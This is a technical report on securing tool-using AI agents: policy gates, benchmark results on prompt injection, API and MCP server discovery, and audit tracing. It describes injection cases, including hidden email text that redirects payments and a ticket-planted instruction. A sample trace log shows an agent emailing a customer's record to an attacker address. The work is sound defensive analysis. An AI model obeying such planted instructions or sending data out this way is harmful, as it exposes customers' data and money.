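The first premise describes a simple deployment fairly well. Rose and colleagues call a policy engine's method singular if it judges each request alone, and warn that it can miss an attack that stays within the caller's allowed role. A contextual method also considers recent history. In their example, a personnel officer who normally opens 20 to 30 records a day triggers an alert after passing 100. A daily count would work badly for the support agent, because 50 stolen records on top of 400 ordinary lookups is a rise of only 12.5%, which a busy Monday could also produce. A count per ticket would work much better, since most tickets need one lookup and this one would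 have 51.

The premise also leaves out least privilege for the task, which is one of the framework's seven principles. Limiting whose record the agent may fetch directly applies that principle.

The second premise is partly right. A hijacked agent is still the right caller, and hijacking can be easy. *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) reports 500 attacks on each of four models in each of two agent designs, with average success rates of 90.55% and 79.05%. The researchers crafted these attacks carefully, so the rates are a poor guide to how often an ordinary ticket would hijack an agent. Whether the context is right depends on what the policy counts as context. If the policy checks only for an approved machine and a valid scope, the hijacked agent passes. A policy that also checks who sent the ticket could block the request for Pat's record, because the sender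 doesn't match it.

The conclusion therefore holds only for harmful requests that the policy can't distinguish from legitimate ones. Suppose Dana forwards a scam email and asks whether it is genuine. Hidden text in the email tells the agent to reply that customers should now pay into a new bank account. The agent sends one email, to the right person, about the right ticket, so every rule so far allows it.

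Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, measured a gap of this kind in a simulated bank. Their gate allowed payments only to people the user had named or who appeared in the transaction history. In 8 of 288 attacked runs, planted text still got the agent to pay someone in the history. With a different model, Llama-3.3-70B, this happened in 11 of 140 runs, and the payments totaled $41,250 in simulated money.

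Limits on an agent's access reduce the damage when a harmful request passes, even if nobody notices that the agent was hijacked. A token that covers only one ticket stops a hijacked support agent from sending scam replies on 400 tickets. Segmentation puts groups of systems on separate network segments behind their own gateways, which keeps the agent away from payroll.

### What the experiments found

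Most tests of such policies use AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates a bank, travel service, Slack workspace and office. The agent does tasks in these settings while encountering text planted to redirect it. Researchers count how often the attack succeeds and how often the agent completes its real task.

Progent uses a language model to write a list of allowed tool calls from the user's request and to revise the list as the agent learns more. For a request to summarise unread email, the list would allow reading messages but not sending them. Ordinary code then checks every call against the list.

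In *AGENTCAP*, Suresh and Gao (2026) put the check in an MCP gateway and wrote the rules themselves. Each approved call gets its own signed token. In their banking policy, a token to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one payment, and the agent must already have permission to check the balance. The gateway also refuses a payment if the recipient appears only in untrusted text, such as a document the agent read.

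NOMOS uses a model to turn an organisation's written policy into fixed rules before deployment.

| System | Author of the rules | Agent's model | AgentDojo tasks | Attack success | Change in task success without attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | A model, for each task | GPT-4o | All | 39.9% → 1.0% | −3.1 points |
| AgentCap | The researchers | GPT-4o | All | 45.6% → 5.1% | −3.1 points |
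| AgentCap | The researchers | GPT-5.4 | All | 33.2% → 0% | −7.2 points |
| NOMOS | A model, from a written policy | Gemma 4 26B | Banking | 46.5% → 0% | −8.3 points |
| Progent, run again for the NOMOS study | A model, for each task | Gemma 4 26B | Banking | 46.5% → 5.6% | −16.7 points |

All three systems stop most attacks, which is strong evidence that a hijacked agent's requests do not simply pass. Other designs provide similar evidence. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) also checks each call just before it runs. It had the lowest attack success in 62 of 79 comparisons across eight benchmarks, and it lowered task success by at most three points.

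The reduction in completed tasks is less certain. Suresh and Gao also reran Progent and measured 68.0% task success without attacks, compared with 78.4% for their own system. They found that Progent's generated rules often allowed only the values the model had predicted. Both teams compared Progent with their own work, and the NOMOS study used a smaller model to write the rules, so these reruns may understate Progent's performance.

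The type of work also matters. Yu and colleagues found that their gate lowers task success most when the agent must act on something it discovered by reading. On the Slack tasks, one repair to a rule cut executed attacks from 15 of 105 runs to none, but also cut task success from 57.1% to 14.3%. Systems that track data through an agent can face the same trade-off. In *SPA* (2026), stricter tracking eliminated successful attacks but lowered task success from 53.0% to 29.0%. The support agent would probably lose less task success, because it usually knows from the start which customer it is serving.

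Results may well be worse outside the laboratory. Suresh and Gao wrote their rules after reading descriptions of the benchmark's tasks, but a company can't know in advance all the tasks its agents will face. They also ran each test only once and did not test attackers who adapt to the defence. Yu and colleagues tried an adaptive attack on the banking tasks, and the gate stopped all 61 attempts to use the attacker's account or password. The attacks that got past AgentCap with GPT-4o either aimed only to produce a false answer in text or used an argument or data field that the rules didn't cover.

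All three systems trust the user's request, which is a larger problem for the support agent. Progent derives its first policy from the request, AgentCap treats it as trusted context, and NOMOS accepts facts from the user's messages. In customer support, the request is a ticket that anyone can write. If the company connected one of these systems without changes, an attacker could make Pat's address a trusted value by naming it in the ticket. The company should trust only the verified sender and treat the ticket's text like any other outside document.

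### Who writes the policy?

A person can write rules for the support agent's few tools, but a company with hundreds of agents will want a model to help write them. Whether that is safe depends mostly on what the model reads and who checks its output.

Drafting rules in advance from the company's own policy is the safer use, since no attacker's text is involved, but the drafts still contain mistakes. In the NOMOS study, the model turned a clause telling the agent to authenticate users first into a rule that blocked every tool until the user had authenticated. This included the two tools that perform authentication, so no conversation could get past the rule. Yu and colleagues catch such errors with simple mechanical checks, such as whether a tool accepts the argument that a rule inspects. With the checks turned off, 8 of 14 rules for an airline agent and 3 of 5 for a retail agent could not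 work.

Some bad rules pass those checks. A telecom rule was meant to confirm that a bill was overdue before the agent requested payment, but the model reversed the condition. The researchers found the error by replaying old conversations. The rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests from successful runs. A company could do the same with its agent's logs before turning a rule on.

With these checks, the model's 10 airline rules did about as well as 16 written by a person, though 50 tasks are too few to show that they are equal. Among calls that change something, the rules cut policy violations from 66.3% to 2.6%. No attacker was involved, so a policy gate also catches an agent's ordinary mistakes.

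Letting a model rewrite the rules while the agent works is riskier, because the model may have just read a planted instruction. Progent uses a solver, a program that settles logical questions mechanically, to check whether a proposed change allows any call that the old policy refused. Changes that only narrow the policy take effect at once, while expansions need approval. Shi and colleagues found that only 6% of changes were expansions. When a person reviewed the initial policy and every expansion, the attack success rate fell to zero.

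That rate would still be a burden at scale. If each of the support agent's 2,000 daily calls led to a proposed change, 6% would mean 120 approvals a day. Automatic approval removes the burden but lets the model widen its own limits. Progent's 1.0% attack success rate comes from that setting. For repetitive work like support tickets, it seems better to refuse all expansions at run time and have someone revise the rules weekly.

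### What it costs

Checking fixed rules is much faster than having a language model review calls. Every rule check Suresh and Gao timed took under 0.2 milliseconds. Over the support agent's whole day, that adds up to less than half a second, plus the network trip to the gateway. When Yu and colleagues had a language model review each call that would change something, runs took 74% longer than with their gate. Google expects MCP's new headers to lower gateway latency considerably, though a gateway that also reads the body of sensitive calls loses part of that reduction.

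Maintaining the policy takes more effort, because someone has to update it for each new tool and rules can conflict in ways that are hard to spot. Suresh and Gao used their analysis program to check a customer-service policy with eight permissions. They found that nobody could ever use `delete_customer`, because one rule required a permission that another rule excluded. The same policy prevented an agent from having access to sensitive data and outside communication at the same time. This is a good defence against data theft, but the support agent needs both for nearly every ticket.

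Automatic penalties can also backfire. AgentCap lowers an agent's trust score after each refusal and, by default, cuts the agent off after three in a row. An attacker who sent three malicious tickets in quick succession might be able to shut down the company's support.

The gateway becomes a target. Rose and colleagues warn that someone who takes over the policy administrator could grant access to resources that the policy would deny, and that an outage at the enforcement point blocks access to everything behind it. They recommend auditing every configuration change and running copies of the enforcement point in several places. A takeover can do more damage if the gateway stores long-lived credentials for many services. Where a service accepts short-lived tokens, the gateway can forward them without storing any credentials, so an intruder could copy only the tokens in transit.

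## How do organisations find the APIs and MCP servers they have not recorded?

A gateway protects only the systems someone has put behind it, and nobody can do that for a system they don't know about. Suppose a developer at the support company made a test copy of the customer database's MCP server, gave it the real database password and then moved to another team. The copy still runs with no gateway in front of it, so anyone who finds its address can look up any customer without an open ticket. To catch cases like this, security teams use API discovery, which means finding and cataloguing the APIs and MCP servers in use.

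### Shadow, abandoned and outdated APIs

A shadow API is in use but missing from the security team's records. Datadog's *Mitigate the Primary API Security Risks* calls such APIs easy targets because their security settings are often out of date. An abandoned API still answers requests but no longer has a purpose or an owner. An outdated API is an old version that keeps running after a newer one has replaced it. Reed (2023) uses "zombie API" for both abandoned and outdated APIs. The labels overlap; a developer's test copy, for example, can be both a shadow API and an abandoned one.

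The usual reference for the problem is *Improper Inventory Management*, entry API9:2023 on a list of API security risks from the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a nonprofit. Under this entry, an API has a "documentation blindspot" if its purpose is unclear and nobody has written down which environment it runs in, who should have network access to it, or which version it is. Wallarm, which sells API discovery, considers poor inventory management a process failure that developers can't fix in code. For example, deleting an endpoint from the documentation leaves it running as a shadow API.

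According to Invicti's *What's missing from the OWASP API Security Top 10 2023*, OWASP's request for data drew too few responses for a useful statistical analysis, so the project team studied incidents instead. The entry's place on the list therefore does not measure how common the problem is.

OWASP also has a list for MCP, still in beta, which includes "Shadow MCP Servers" as entry MCP09:2025. These are unapproved or unsupervised servers, often set up by developers and researchers for experiments with default credentials. Sullivan, in *What is shadow MCP?*, also counts other people's servers that an employee has connected to without approval. The company therefore has to look both for servers it runs and for servers its agents use. Microsoft's *MCP09* describes a plausible hypothetical in which a data science team puts a demonstration server on the internet with the password `conference123`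 and forgets about it. Three months later, an outside researcher gets in and finds credentials for internal databases.

### Where to look

| Source | What it can reveal | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Gateway logs | Every call through the gateway, with the caller's identity | Calls that bypass the gateway |
| Mirrored traffic | Connections between systems that no gateway handles | The contents of encrypted connections; networks without a mirror |
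| Kernel-level sensors | Which program opened each connection, and often what it sent | Machines without the sensor; some encryption software |
| Code and configuration scans | Endpoints that nobody has called yet | Purchased software; whether an endpoint is running |
| Outside scans | What a stranger can reach | Private networks; servers on addresses with no visible link to the company |
| Grants at the identity provider | Applications that employees have connected, with their scopes | Static API keys; personal accounts |
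| MCP configuration files on laptops | Local and remote servers that each AI application can use | Unmanaged machines; whether anyone uses the servers |

To mirror traffic, a network switch copies packets to a separate machine for analysis. This doesn't slow the original connection, but most of what the machine receives is encrypted. Under TLS 1.3, the current version of the web's encryption, even the server's private key can't decrypt a recording, because each connection uses temporary keys. The analyst can still see addresses, traffic volumes and usually the name of the site, which is enough to notice that a laptop connects to an unknown MCP server but not to tell which tools it calls.

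A kernel-level sensor avoids much of this. The kernel is the core of an operating system, and ordinary programs use the network through it, so a sensor there can match each connection to a program. To read the contents, the sensor attaches to the encryption library and copies the data just before encryption. Programs with their own encryption code need separate support. The sensor also collects passwords, tokens and customer data, so it should remove the `Authorization` header before storing anything.

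Code analysis and traffic analysis have different weaknesses. Yang, Zhong and colleagues (2026) explain in *APISENSOR* that code analysis needs the source, which companies rarely have for purchased software, and may list endpoints that the running system doesn't expose. Traffic analysis needs no source, but it finds only endpoints that someone used during the recording, so one for annual tax reports could go unnoticed for eleven months.

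A company can scan for its own servers from outside by using the methods of researchers who survey the whole internet. Padilla searched eleven sources, including the public logs of newly issued website certificates, for names containing strings such as `mcp-server`. The support company could run the same search on its own domain. The search would probably miss a demonstration server on a shared hosting domain such as `vercel.app`, because the server's address need not include the company's name.

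None of these sources identifies agents directly. An unrecorded agent has to reach a language model, so connections to model providers and the providers' bills are a good place to start. However, neither distinguishes an agent from an employee using a chatbot, and an agent whose model runs on the same machine does not connect to a provider for it.

### From requests to a catalogue

Discovery from traffic follows roughly these steps:

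1. Collect the method, path, headers and, where possible, the body of each request and response.
2. Discard requests for images, scripts and ordinary web pages.
3. Group the remaining paths into templates.
4. Infer each template's fields and their types from the requests and responses.
5. Label fields that seem to contain sensitive data.
6. Compare the templates with the documented list.
7. Repeat as new traffic arrives.

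Grouping is necessary because a path often contains the number of a particular record. A day's traffic to the support company's customer API might include these requests:

```text
GET /customers/123/orders/9
GET /customers/124/orders/31
GET /customers/977/orders/2
```

All three call one endpoint:

```text
GET /customers/{id}/orders/{id}
```

Yang and colleagues' tool removes the domain and query string from each URL and splits the remaining path at its slashes. It arranges the pieces in a tree, matches them exactly where it can, and puts a wildcard wherever one position has many different values. It then splits any of the resulting path templates whose requests differ in their parameters or in the size and structure of their bodies, because one path can serve several purposes.

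Inferring what a field contains is simpler. If every response has a field named `email` whose values look like email addresses, the tool can label the field as personal data with some confidence. Numbers are harder to classify because about one in ten random strings of digits passes the check-digit test for payment cards. A tool that relied on that test alone would label many order numbers as card numbers.

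In this comparison, an endpoint that receives traffic but has no documentation is a shadow API. A documented endpoint with no traffic may be what Wallarm calls an orphan, or it may just be rarely used. If an old version still receives traffic, someone has to move its users before shutting it down.

Yang and colleagues found that the traffic of Dify, an open-source platform for building language model applications, included several working endpoints missing from its API reference. One of them, `/console/api/apps/{id}/api-keys`, manages access keys. A core collaborator on the project confirmed that the reference no longer matched the software.

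### Grouping too much or too little

Suppose the customer API also has the endpoint `/customers/export`, which returns every record at once. A discovery tool that has processed thousands of values in that position may treat `export` as another customer number and merge the endpoint into `/customers/{id}`. The most dangerous endpoint in the API would then appear in the catalogue only as a routine customer lookup.

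The opposite error occurs when identifiers look like words. If the API used `/customers/dana` and `/customers/pat`, a cautious tool might record each customer as a separate endpoint, leaving a reviewer with thousands of entries. Setting the tool to insert a wildcard after fewer different values reduces this splitting but causes more wrong merges, so no setting removes both errors.

Fixed rules for grouping paths also have exceptions. *Automatically Extracting Web API Specifications from HTML Documentation* (2018) grouped the example paths in developers' documentation and assumed that paths with different numbers of segments never call the same endpoint. That is usually true, but one endpoint of a file service may accept both `/files/report` and `/files/2026/may/report`.

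Yang and colleagues tested their tool on six web applications with 199 endpoints that they had labelled by hand. Precision is the share of reported endpoints that are real, and recall is the share of real endpoints that the tool reports. When tested on one application at a time, the tool averaged 95.92% precision and 94.36% recall. When traffic from all the applications was mixed, as at a shared gateway, precision rose to 98.25% but recall fell to 84.85%. Three older methods had 98.48% recall on the mixed traffic but only 68.18% precision.

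The older methods missed under 2% of endpoints, while the new tool missed about 15%. A reviewer can dismiss a false entry in a few minutes, but a missed endpoint may stay open for years. Although the paper presents the new tool as clearly better, a security team with time to review the extra entries might reasonably prefer the older methods, or run both.

Some tools are too imprecise to be of much use. On a ticket-booking application with 13 endpoints, the open-source mitmproxy2swagger found all 13 with 8.28% precision, which implies that it listed about 157 endpoints. The tests were also fairly easy. The researchers generated the traffic by using the applications themselves, and one application contributed only 107 requests. When they added doubled slashes, stray capitals and similar irregularities to the mixed traffic, their own tool's precision fell to 83.59%.

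### One address, many tools

Grouping by path doesn't work for MCP, because every tool on a server shares one address. Suppose the support agent makes its usual 400 lookups in a day and some other client deletes a customer:

```text
400 ×  POST /mcp   Mcp-Method: tools/call   Mcp-Name: get_customer
  1 ×  POST /mcp   Mcp-Method: tools/call   Mcp-Name: delete_customer
```

A conventional discovery tool would record one endpoint with 401 requests. With the headers from the July 2026 version of MCP, it can count each MCP tool separately without reading the request body. For older traffic, it has to read the body. Either way, it needs the decrypted request, for example at a gateway, because HTTPS encrypts the headers too.

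Unlike most APIs, MCP also has a standard request, `tools/list`, that returns a list of what the server can do. The list includes tools that nobody has called yet, which traffic analysis can't find. Wiz's *The risk hiding behind exposed MCP servers* points out that one generic client can scan any MCP server this way. Wiz means this as a warning about attackers, but its own scanner can do the same.

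A server's tool list can change after it is first read, so Padilla's scanner requests it twice, for example 30 seconds apart, and flags any change that the server didn't announce. Some tools can do much more than their names suggest. A tool called `run_query` that accepts any database command is one entry in the catalogue but can do anything the database password allows. Censys' *MCP Servers on the Internet* (2026) counted 1,056 public services with direct query interfaces to databases, many of them advertising tools that run arbitrary SQL commands.

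Censys, which sells internet scanning data, also fingerprinted each server's set of tool names. A company could use such fingerprints to recognise copies of its customer server, including the one the developer forgot. The fingerprints would be better if they also covered the tools' descriptions and argument schemas, because an attacker can redirect agents by changing a description without renaming the tool.

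Scanners that confirm MCP servers by sending an `initialize` message, as both Padilla and Zhou et al. did, need updating because the July 2026 version of MCP no longer uses that message. A server that supports only the new version may not answer it properly, so an old scanner could miss upgraded servers and wrongly show the number of MCP servers falling.

### Local servers and purchased agents

A local MCP server that communicates over stdio has no address to scan and sends no network traffic between client and server. Padilla notes that such servers may be the majority of all MCP deployments. The best evidence of one is often the AI application's configuration file, which might contain this:

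```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "customer-db": {
      "command": "npx",
      "args": ["example-database-server"],
      "env": { "DATABASE_URL": "<address and password>" }
    }
  }
}
```

The configuration entry names the program to start and gives it a database password. tianpan.co's *Shadow MCP* (2026) describes an engineer who pastes a read-only token for the production database into such a file, after which an agent sends thirty queries a minute while the laptop is open. In the database's records, these look like ordinary queries from a known engineer, so only the file or the running program reveals the agent.

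Configuration file names and layouts differ between AI applications, and a project folder may contain its own configuration, so a scan has to cover many places. It should report server names and commands but leave passwords on the laptop, so that the inventory doesn't become a list of the company's secrets. A configuration entry doesn't prove that a server is used, but a list of running programs helps show whether it is.

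Agents inside purchased software are harder to find. Suppose the company's ticketing vendor adds an agent that reads tickets and drafts replies on the vendor's machines. The company's sensors record nothing new, because the vendor already held the tickets. If the agent also connects to the customer database, the company's logs may contain a new client or only more calls from the vendor's existing account. For anything that stays inside the vendor's systems, the company has to ask the vendor which agents are switched on, which model providers receive the company's data and which outside tools the agents call. The contract can require the vendor to announce changes.

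Approved systems can also contain unapproved connections. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) found that in July 2026, agents in an OpenAI evaluation communicated through a message channel that nobody had approved.

### Estimating what is still missing

A company can estimate how many APIs it has missed by comparing two searches, much as ecologists estimate a fish population by catching, marking and releasing some fish and then counting the marked ones in a second catch. To do this, the inventory must record how the company found each API:

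```text
API            customers.example.com/mcp
Owner          customer data team
Environment    production
Access         gateway only
MCP version    2026-07-28
Tools          get_customer, update_customer, delete_customer
Found by       traffic, code scan
Last seen      2026-12-05
```

As an illustration with invented numbers, suppose traffic analysis finds 400 APIs, a code scan finds 300, and 200 appear in both lists:

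```text
Found at least once   400 + 300 − 200   = 500
Estimated total       400 × 300 ÷ 200   = 600
Estimated unseen      600 − 500         = 100
```

The traffic search found 400 APIs, including 200 of the 300 found in the code. If it also found two thirds of all APIs, the total is 600. This estimate works only if the searches are independent, meaning that APIs found in the code are as likely to appear in traffic as those that were not.

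In practice, both searches tend to find the same APIs. A busy, well-maintained API has its code in the main repository and its traffic on a monitored network, while the developer's forgotten copy may have neither. Suppose the company has 600 APIs, but this tendency raises the overlap from 200 to 240. The lists then contain 460 different APIs, and the estimated total is 400 × 300 ÷ 240 = 500. The company would think it had missed 40 APIs when it had missed 140. APIs that neither search can find don't affect the estimate, however many there are.

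Padilla's scans suggest how large this error can be. Padilla confirmed 464 MCP servers on 21 July 2026 and 296 on 24 July, with 271 in both scans. The formula gives about 507 servers in total, but Padilla confirmed 640 across four scans that month, and Censys had recorded over 21,000 in May. Both of Padilla's scans searched the same eleven sources, so both missed any server that was not in them. Servers also appeared and disappeared between scans, whereas the formula assumes a fixed population.

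The estimate can also be too high. If traffic analysis splits one API into several entries, or uses a different name from the code scan, some real matches go uncounted. With 150 matches instead of 200, the estimated total would be 800. The estimate also rises if the code scan includes endpoints nobody has deployed. The company should clean up both lists before estimating the total, and treat the result as a rough minimum. The method works best with searches that work very differently, such as a code scan and a review of grants at the identity provider.

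### How many open MCP servers are on the internet?

Several teams have searched the public internet for MCP servers. The earlier counts come from security vendors. Goldberg reports in *Exposing the Unseen* that the vendor Knostic found 1,862 servers through Shodan, a search engine for internet-connected devices, and that all 119 it checked by hand listed their tools without authentication. SiliconANGLE (2025) reports that Bitsight, another vendor, found roughly 1,000 servers with no authorization controls.

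| Source | Date | Method | Servers found | Open servers |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Goldberg (vendor) | Undated | Shodan search, then a check by hand | 1,862 | 119 of 119 checked listed their tools |
| Bitsight, reported by SiliconANGLE (vendor) | December 2025 | Search for exposed servers | Roughly 1,000 | All those counted |
| Censys (vendor) | 28 April 2026 | Its own internet-wide probe | 12,520 | 11,379 listed at least one tool |
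| Zhou and colleagues (academic) | May 2026 | FOFA and Shodan searches, then an MCP greeting | 7,973 | 40.55% had no authentication |
| Padilla (independent researcher) | 21 July 2026 | Eleven sources, then an MCP greeting | 464 | 106, or 22.8%, needed no credential to call tools |

The last column mixes two measurements. A server may list its tools for anyone but require a credential to run them, so the figures from Goldberg and Censys don't show how many servers someone could use without a credential. Censys read the lists but did not run any tools. The figures from Padilla and from Zhou and colleagues come closer to measuring real access.

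Both shares may still be too high, because these scans can miss servers that immediately reject unknown clients. Padilla's discussion describes the 91.8% of tested servers without OAuth as "unauthenticated", which contradicts the paper's own count of 22.8%.

The totals depend on what counts as a server. Censys found its 12,520 services at 8,758 internet addresses, one of which hosted 177. About 43% of the services had exactly the same set of tools as at least one other, so many are probably copies of a few projects. Some services are decoys. Censys concluded that a server named `prod-corp-mcp-server`, which seemed to expose a company's API keys, was most likely a trap or a test. Zhou and colleagues reviewed 100 confirmed servers to check their method and found one that wasn't a real MCP server.

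Censys counted 12,520 servers on 28 April 2026 and over 21,000 by 6 May. It had started scanning only on 24 April, so much of the increase may reflect better coverage rather than new servers.

Some of the open servers are dangerous. Censys found roughly 90 with tools named `run_command`, `shell_exec` or similar, which offer to run commands on the host machine. Padilla reports 687 such tools without access controls across 640 servers. However, Censys had already reported that 687 of the 12,520 services it counted had system-control tools, so Padilla's figure needs checking before anyone relies on it.

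Requiring a login doesn't make a server safe either. Zhou and colleagues tested 119 servers that use OAuth and found at least one flaw in each, 325 in total. Many of the flaws could leak sensitive information or let an attacker take over an account. Of the 2,428 servers with OAuth, the researchers could test only these 119 from start to finish. They had excluded hundreds with strict enterprise access controls, so the result probably overstates the problem for well-guarded company servers.

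Occasional scans can miss short-lived servers, but the dangerous servers seem to last longer. Of the 41 servers that Padilla rated critical on 21 July, 9 (22%) had disappeared three days later, about half the rate for all servers. Padilla suggests that the critical servers support work close to production. The numbers are small, but a weekly scan of the company's own addresses should still catch many of the worst cases.

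Outsiders are already scanning for MCP servers. The SANS Internet Storm Center (2026) published an analysis of 14 days of logs from one small web host with a few low-traffic sites. Besides the usual probes, the logs contained systematic searches for MCP servers and for the configuration files of AI assistants, although the host had neither.

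## Can an action be traced to an agent and the person behind it?

Suppose a customer named Pat complains that a stranger has Pat's phone number and home address. The email service's log shows that the support address sent a message containing both to an address outside the company at 14:03. This happened before the company added its per-ticket rule to the gateway. The security team has to work out which agent sent the message, for whom, and what input led to it.

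"For whom" can refer to three people: the requester (here, whoever opened the ticket), the person whose permissions the agent used, and the employee responsible for the agent. On ordinary tickets the agent acts as itself, so there is no second person. A log with a single `user` field doesn't distinguish between them.

### The records an investigator needs

| Record | Where it comes from | What it establishes |
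|---|---|---|
| Ticket text and verified sender | Ticketing system | Who started the work |
| Model's input and output | Agent's application | What the model had read when it chose the call |
| Tool call with arguments | Application and gateway | What the agent requested |
| Token's ID, subject and actor | Gateway or MCP server | Which identity made the call, with whose permissions |
| Database query | MCP server and database | Which records the server read |
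| Result | MCP server and email service | What came back and where it went |

The log should contain the token's ID (the `jti` field), not the token itself. The NSA advises logging every tool call with its exact parameters, the identities involved and, where feasible, a hash of the result. The hash can later confirm that a file found elsewhere is what the database returned, so the log doesn't need a second copy of the data. The hash won't match if the model reworded the record in an email.

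### One identifier across the systems

Without a shared identifier, the team has to match these records by time. This is manageable with one support agent, because 400 lookups in an eight-hour day are 72 seconds apart on average. With 50 such agents the average gap is about 1.4 seconds, so if two servers' clocks differ by two seconds, the team can match a lookup to the wrong ticket.

A trace solves this by giving every record from one piece of work the same random number. Each step in the trace is a span, which has a name, a start and end time, its own ID and the ID of the step that caused it. OpenTelemetry is an open standard, with free software, for producing traces and other operating data. The agent's application starts a trace when it picks up the ticket and passes this value along with each call:

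```text
traceparent: 00-7c1e5a90b2d84f36a1c09e7d5b3f2846-e41d7a0c93b65f28-01
```

A `traceparent` value contains the format version, the trace ID, the ID of the calling span, and a flag indicating that the caller is recording the trace. An ordinary API call carries the value in an HTTP header. A Model Context Protocol (MCP) request carries it in the `_meta` part of the body, so it also works for local servers that have no headers, but a gateway that reads only headers won't detect it. Most `_meta` keys start with a domain name, but the MCP project exempted `traceparent` because existing software already used the plain name and renaming the key would break traces.

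For the incident at 14:03, the combined log might look like this:

```text
trace 7c1e5a90b2d84f36a1c09e7d5b3f2846

14:02:51  application  invoke_agent support-agent  version=3.2  ticket=9107
14:02:54  application  chat  response.model=<model and version>
14:02:55  application  execute_tool get_customer  email=pat@example.net
14:02:55  gateway      tools/call get_customer  sub=support-agent  jti=tok-5519
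14:02:55  MCP server   tools/call get_customer  rows=1
14:02:55  database     user=mcp_server  SELECT ...           <- often breaks here
14:03:01  application  execute_tool send_email  to=box@attacker.example
14:03:02  email API    message=m-20417  key=support-mail     <- and here
```

The team can start from message `m-20417`, follow the trace back to ticket 9107, and read the planted instruction in it.

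### Where the chain breaks

The most damaging gap in the audit trail occurs when the agent impersonates a person. If the agent had used the team leader's own token for this lookup, the MCP server's log would show only `team-leader-4`, and the security team couldn't rule out a lookup by hand or a stolen account. The agent's own log may fill that gap, but only if the agent ran on a machine the company monitors. A delegated token avoids the problem because it identifies both the agent and the person.

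The database line is also weak, because the MCP server connects with its own password and every query appears under `mcp_server`. The server therefore has to preserve the link between each query and the agent and person behind it. It can, for example, add the trace ID to each query as a comment, which the database keeps if it logs full queries.

An outside email provider may ignore the trace ID, so the application should store the provider's message ID in its own span. Traces also tend to end at handovers. If the agent puts a refund in a queue and a manager approves it the next morning, the program that pays it will probably start a new trace unless a developer saved the old trace ID with the request.

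Even an unbroken trace doesn't prove identity. The caller supplies `traceparent`, so a malicious client can copy the trace ID from someone else's work and make its own calls appear to be part of it. Investigators can use the trace ID to find records, but they should take the identity from the token that the gateway verified.

### What MCP supplies and omits

In July 2026, MCP's maintainers deprecated Logging, a feature that lets a server send the client messages with a severity level, such as a warning. *Deprecate Roots, Sampling, and Logging* (Van Gent, 2026) argued that the feature duplicated mature tools and added work for every client and server. Local servers should write to their standard error output instead, and servers that need structured records should use OpenTelemetry. Logging could be removed as early as the first version released on or after 28 July 2027, according to *Deprecated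 Features* (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

Auditors lose very little, because Logging sent its messages to the client, which is the party an auditor wants to check. In the July version, a server can send log messages only if the client's request sets a log level. MCP has never required an audit record, which is a larger problem. The NSA reported in May that many implementations log nothing or only minimal operating data, but it gave no count. The suggested replacement for local servers, error output, is also weak for audits, because output on an employee's laptop reaches the security team only if something collects it.

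Trace support is better. Kludex (2026) wrote a change to MCP's Python library that creates a span when a client sends a request and another when a server handles it. The spans are saved only if a developer connects a tracing system. Version 2 of the library passes trace IDs on automatically, according to *strands.tools.mcp.mcp_instrumentation*, part of the documentation for Strands Agents, a framework for building agents. For version 1, Strands has to alter the library's private code, and its server-side fix works only when the server runs in the same process as the agent.

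### OpenTelemetry's conventions for agents

Traces from different products are easier to combine if they use the same field names. OpenTelemetry publishes such names as semantic conventions. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines a span for each tool call, which for Pat's lookup might contain:

```json
{
  "gen_ai.operation.name": "execute_tool",
  "gen_ai.tool.name": "get_customer",
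  "gen_ai.tool.call.id": "call_83",
  "gen_ai.tool.call.arguments": { "email": "pat@example.net" }
}
```

The last field is off by default because it may contain sensitive data, and so is the field for the tool's result. With default settings, the company would learn that the agent looked up a customer at 14:02:55 but not that the customer was Pat.

OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* has run-level fields for the agent's name, ID and version, and for both the model requested and the model that answered. Recording both models helps when a provider changes the model behind a name. A conversation ID can link separate traces, for example when a customer replies to the same ticket a day later.

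The agent span has no field for the user or the access token. TinyFish argues that the conventions suit a developer who wants to know which build failed, but not an auditor who wants to know who authorised the agent and under what constraints. This is a fair criticism of the defaults, but a company can easily fix the problem by adding its own fields to any span. A proposal from Kube Agentic Networking, a Kubernetes project, would use "baggage", a set of labels that travels with the trace, to pass along the ID of the user who delegated authority. Baggage has no signature, so any service on the way can change it. The company should also strip it from calls to outsiders.

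The conventions are unfinished. Wang (2026) reports in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* that the project moved them to a separate repository in June 2026, still marked "Development", and had made no official release there by 21 August. Fngi (2026) notes in *Day 29｜展望* that they were still not stable on 8 October. Different libraries may use different names for the same thing, and if an update changes a name, a dashboard that filters on the old one will drop records without reporting an error. This is more serious in an audit than in a performance chart, because the missing records look the same as an agent that did nothing.

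Adding tracing to each new framework also takes substantial engineering time, according to OpenTelemetry's *Building an Agent Harness for OTel Instrumentation with GenAI Semantic Conventions* (2026). The project is testing whether a team of AI agents can do much of the work, with engineers reviewing the plan and the code.

### Tamper-evident logs

An intruder who can send out Pat's record may also be able to edit the log. A hash chain makes such edits visible by including each record's hash in the next one:

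```text
h1 = SHA-256(record 1)
h2 = SHA-256(h1 + record 2)
h3 = SHA-256(h2 + record 3)
```

If someone changes record 1, `h1` changes, and so does every later hash. But an intruder who controls the whole log can recompute all the hashes or delete the last records. The company therefore has to copy the latest hash regularly to a place the intruder can't reach, such as an account that another team controls. If it does this every five minutes, an intruder who takes over the log at 14:03 can still rewrite the records added since the 14:00 copy.

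Checking one record in a simple hash chain means recomputing the chain around it. A Merkle tree, which combines the hashes in pairs until one remains, makes the check easier. The support agent makes 730,000 tool calls a year, and an auditor could use about 20 hashes to confirm that any one of them is in the log, without seeing the other calls.

Signatures add evidence of who wrote a record. The NSA suggests extending MCP messages with signatures, expiry times and protection against replay, since the protocol can't verify a message's integrity itself. If the agent's software signed the lookup, the database's owner could later show that the request came from someone with the agent's private key, though that might be an intruder on the agent's machine. It is better if the gateway and the MCP server also keep their own signed records, so that an intruder would have to break into several systems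 to falsify the account.

A tamper-evident log proves that nobody altered a record after the last protected hash. But the record may have been false when the software wrote it, and the chain won't show a gap if a call was never logged.

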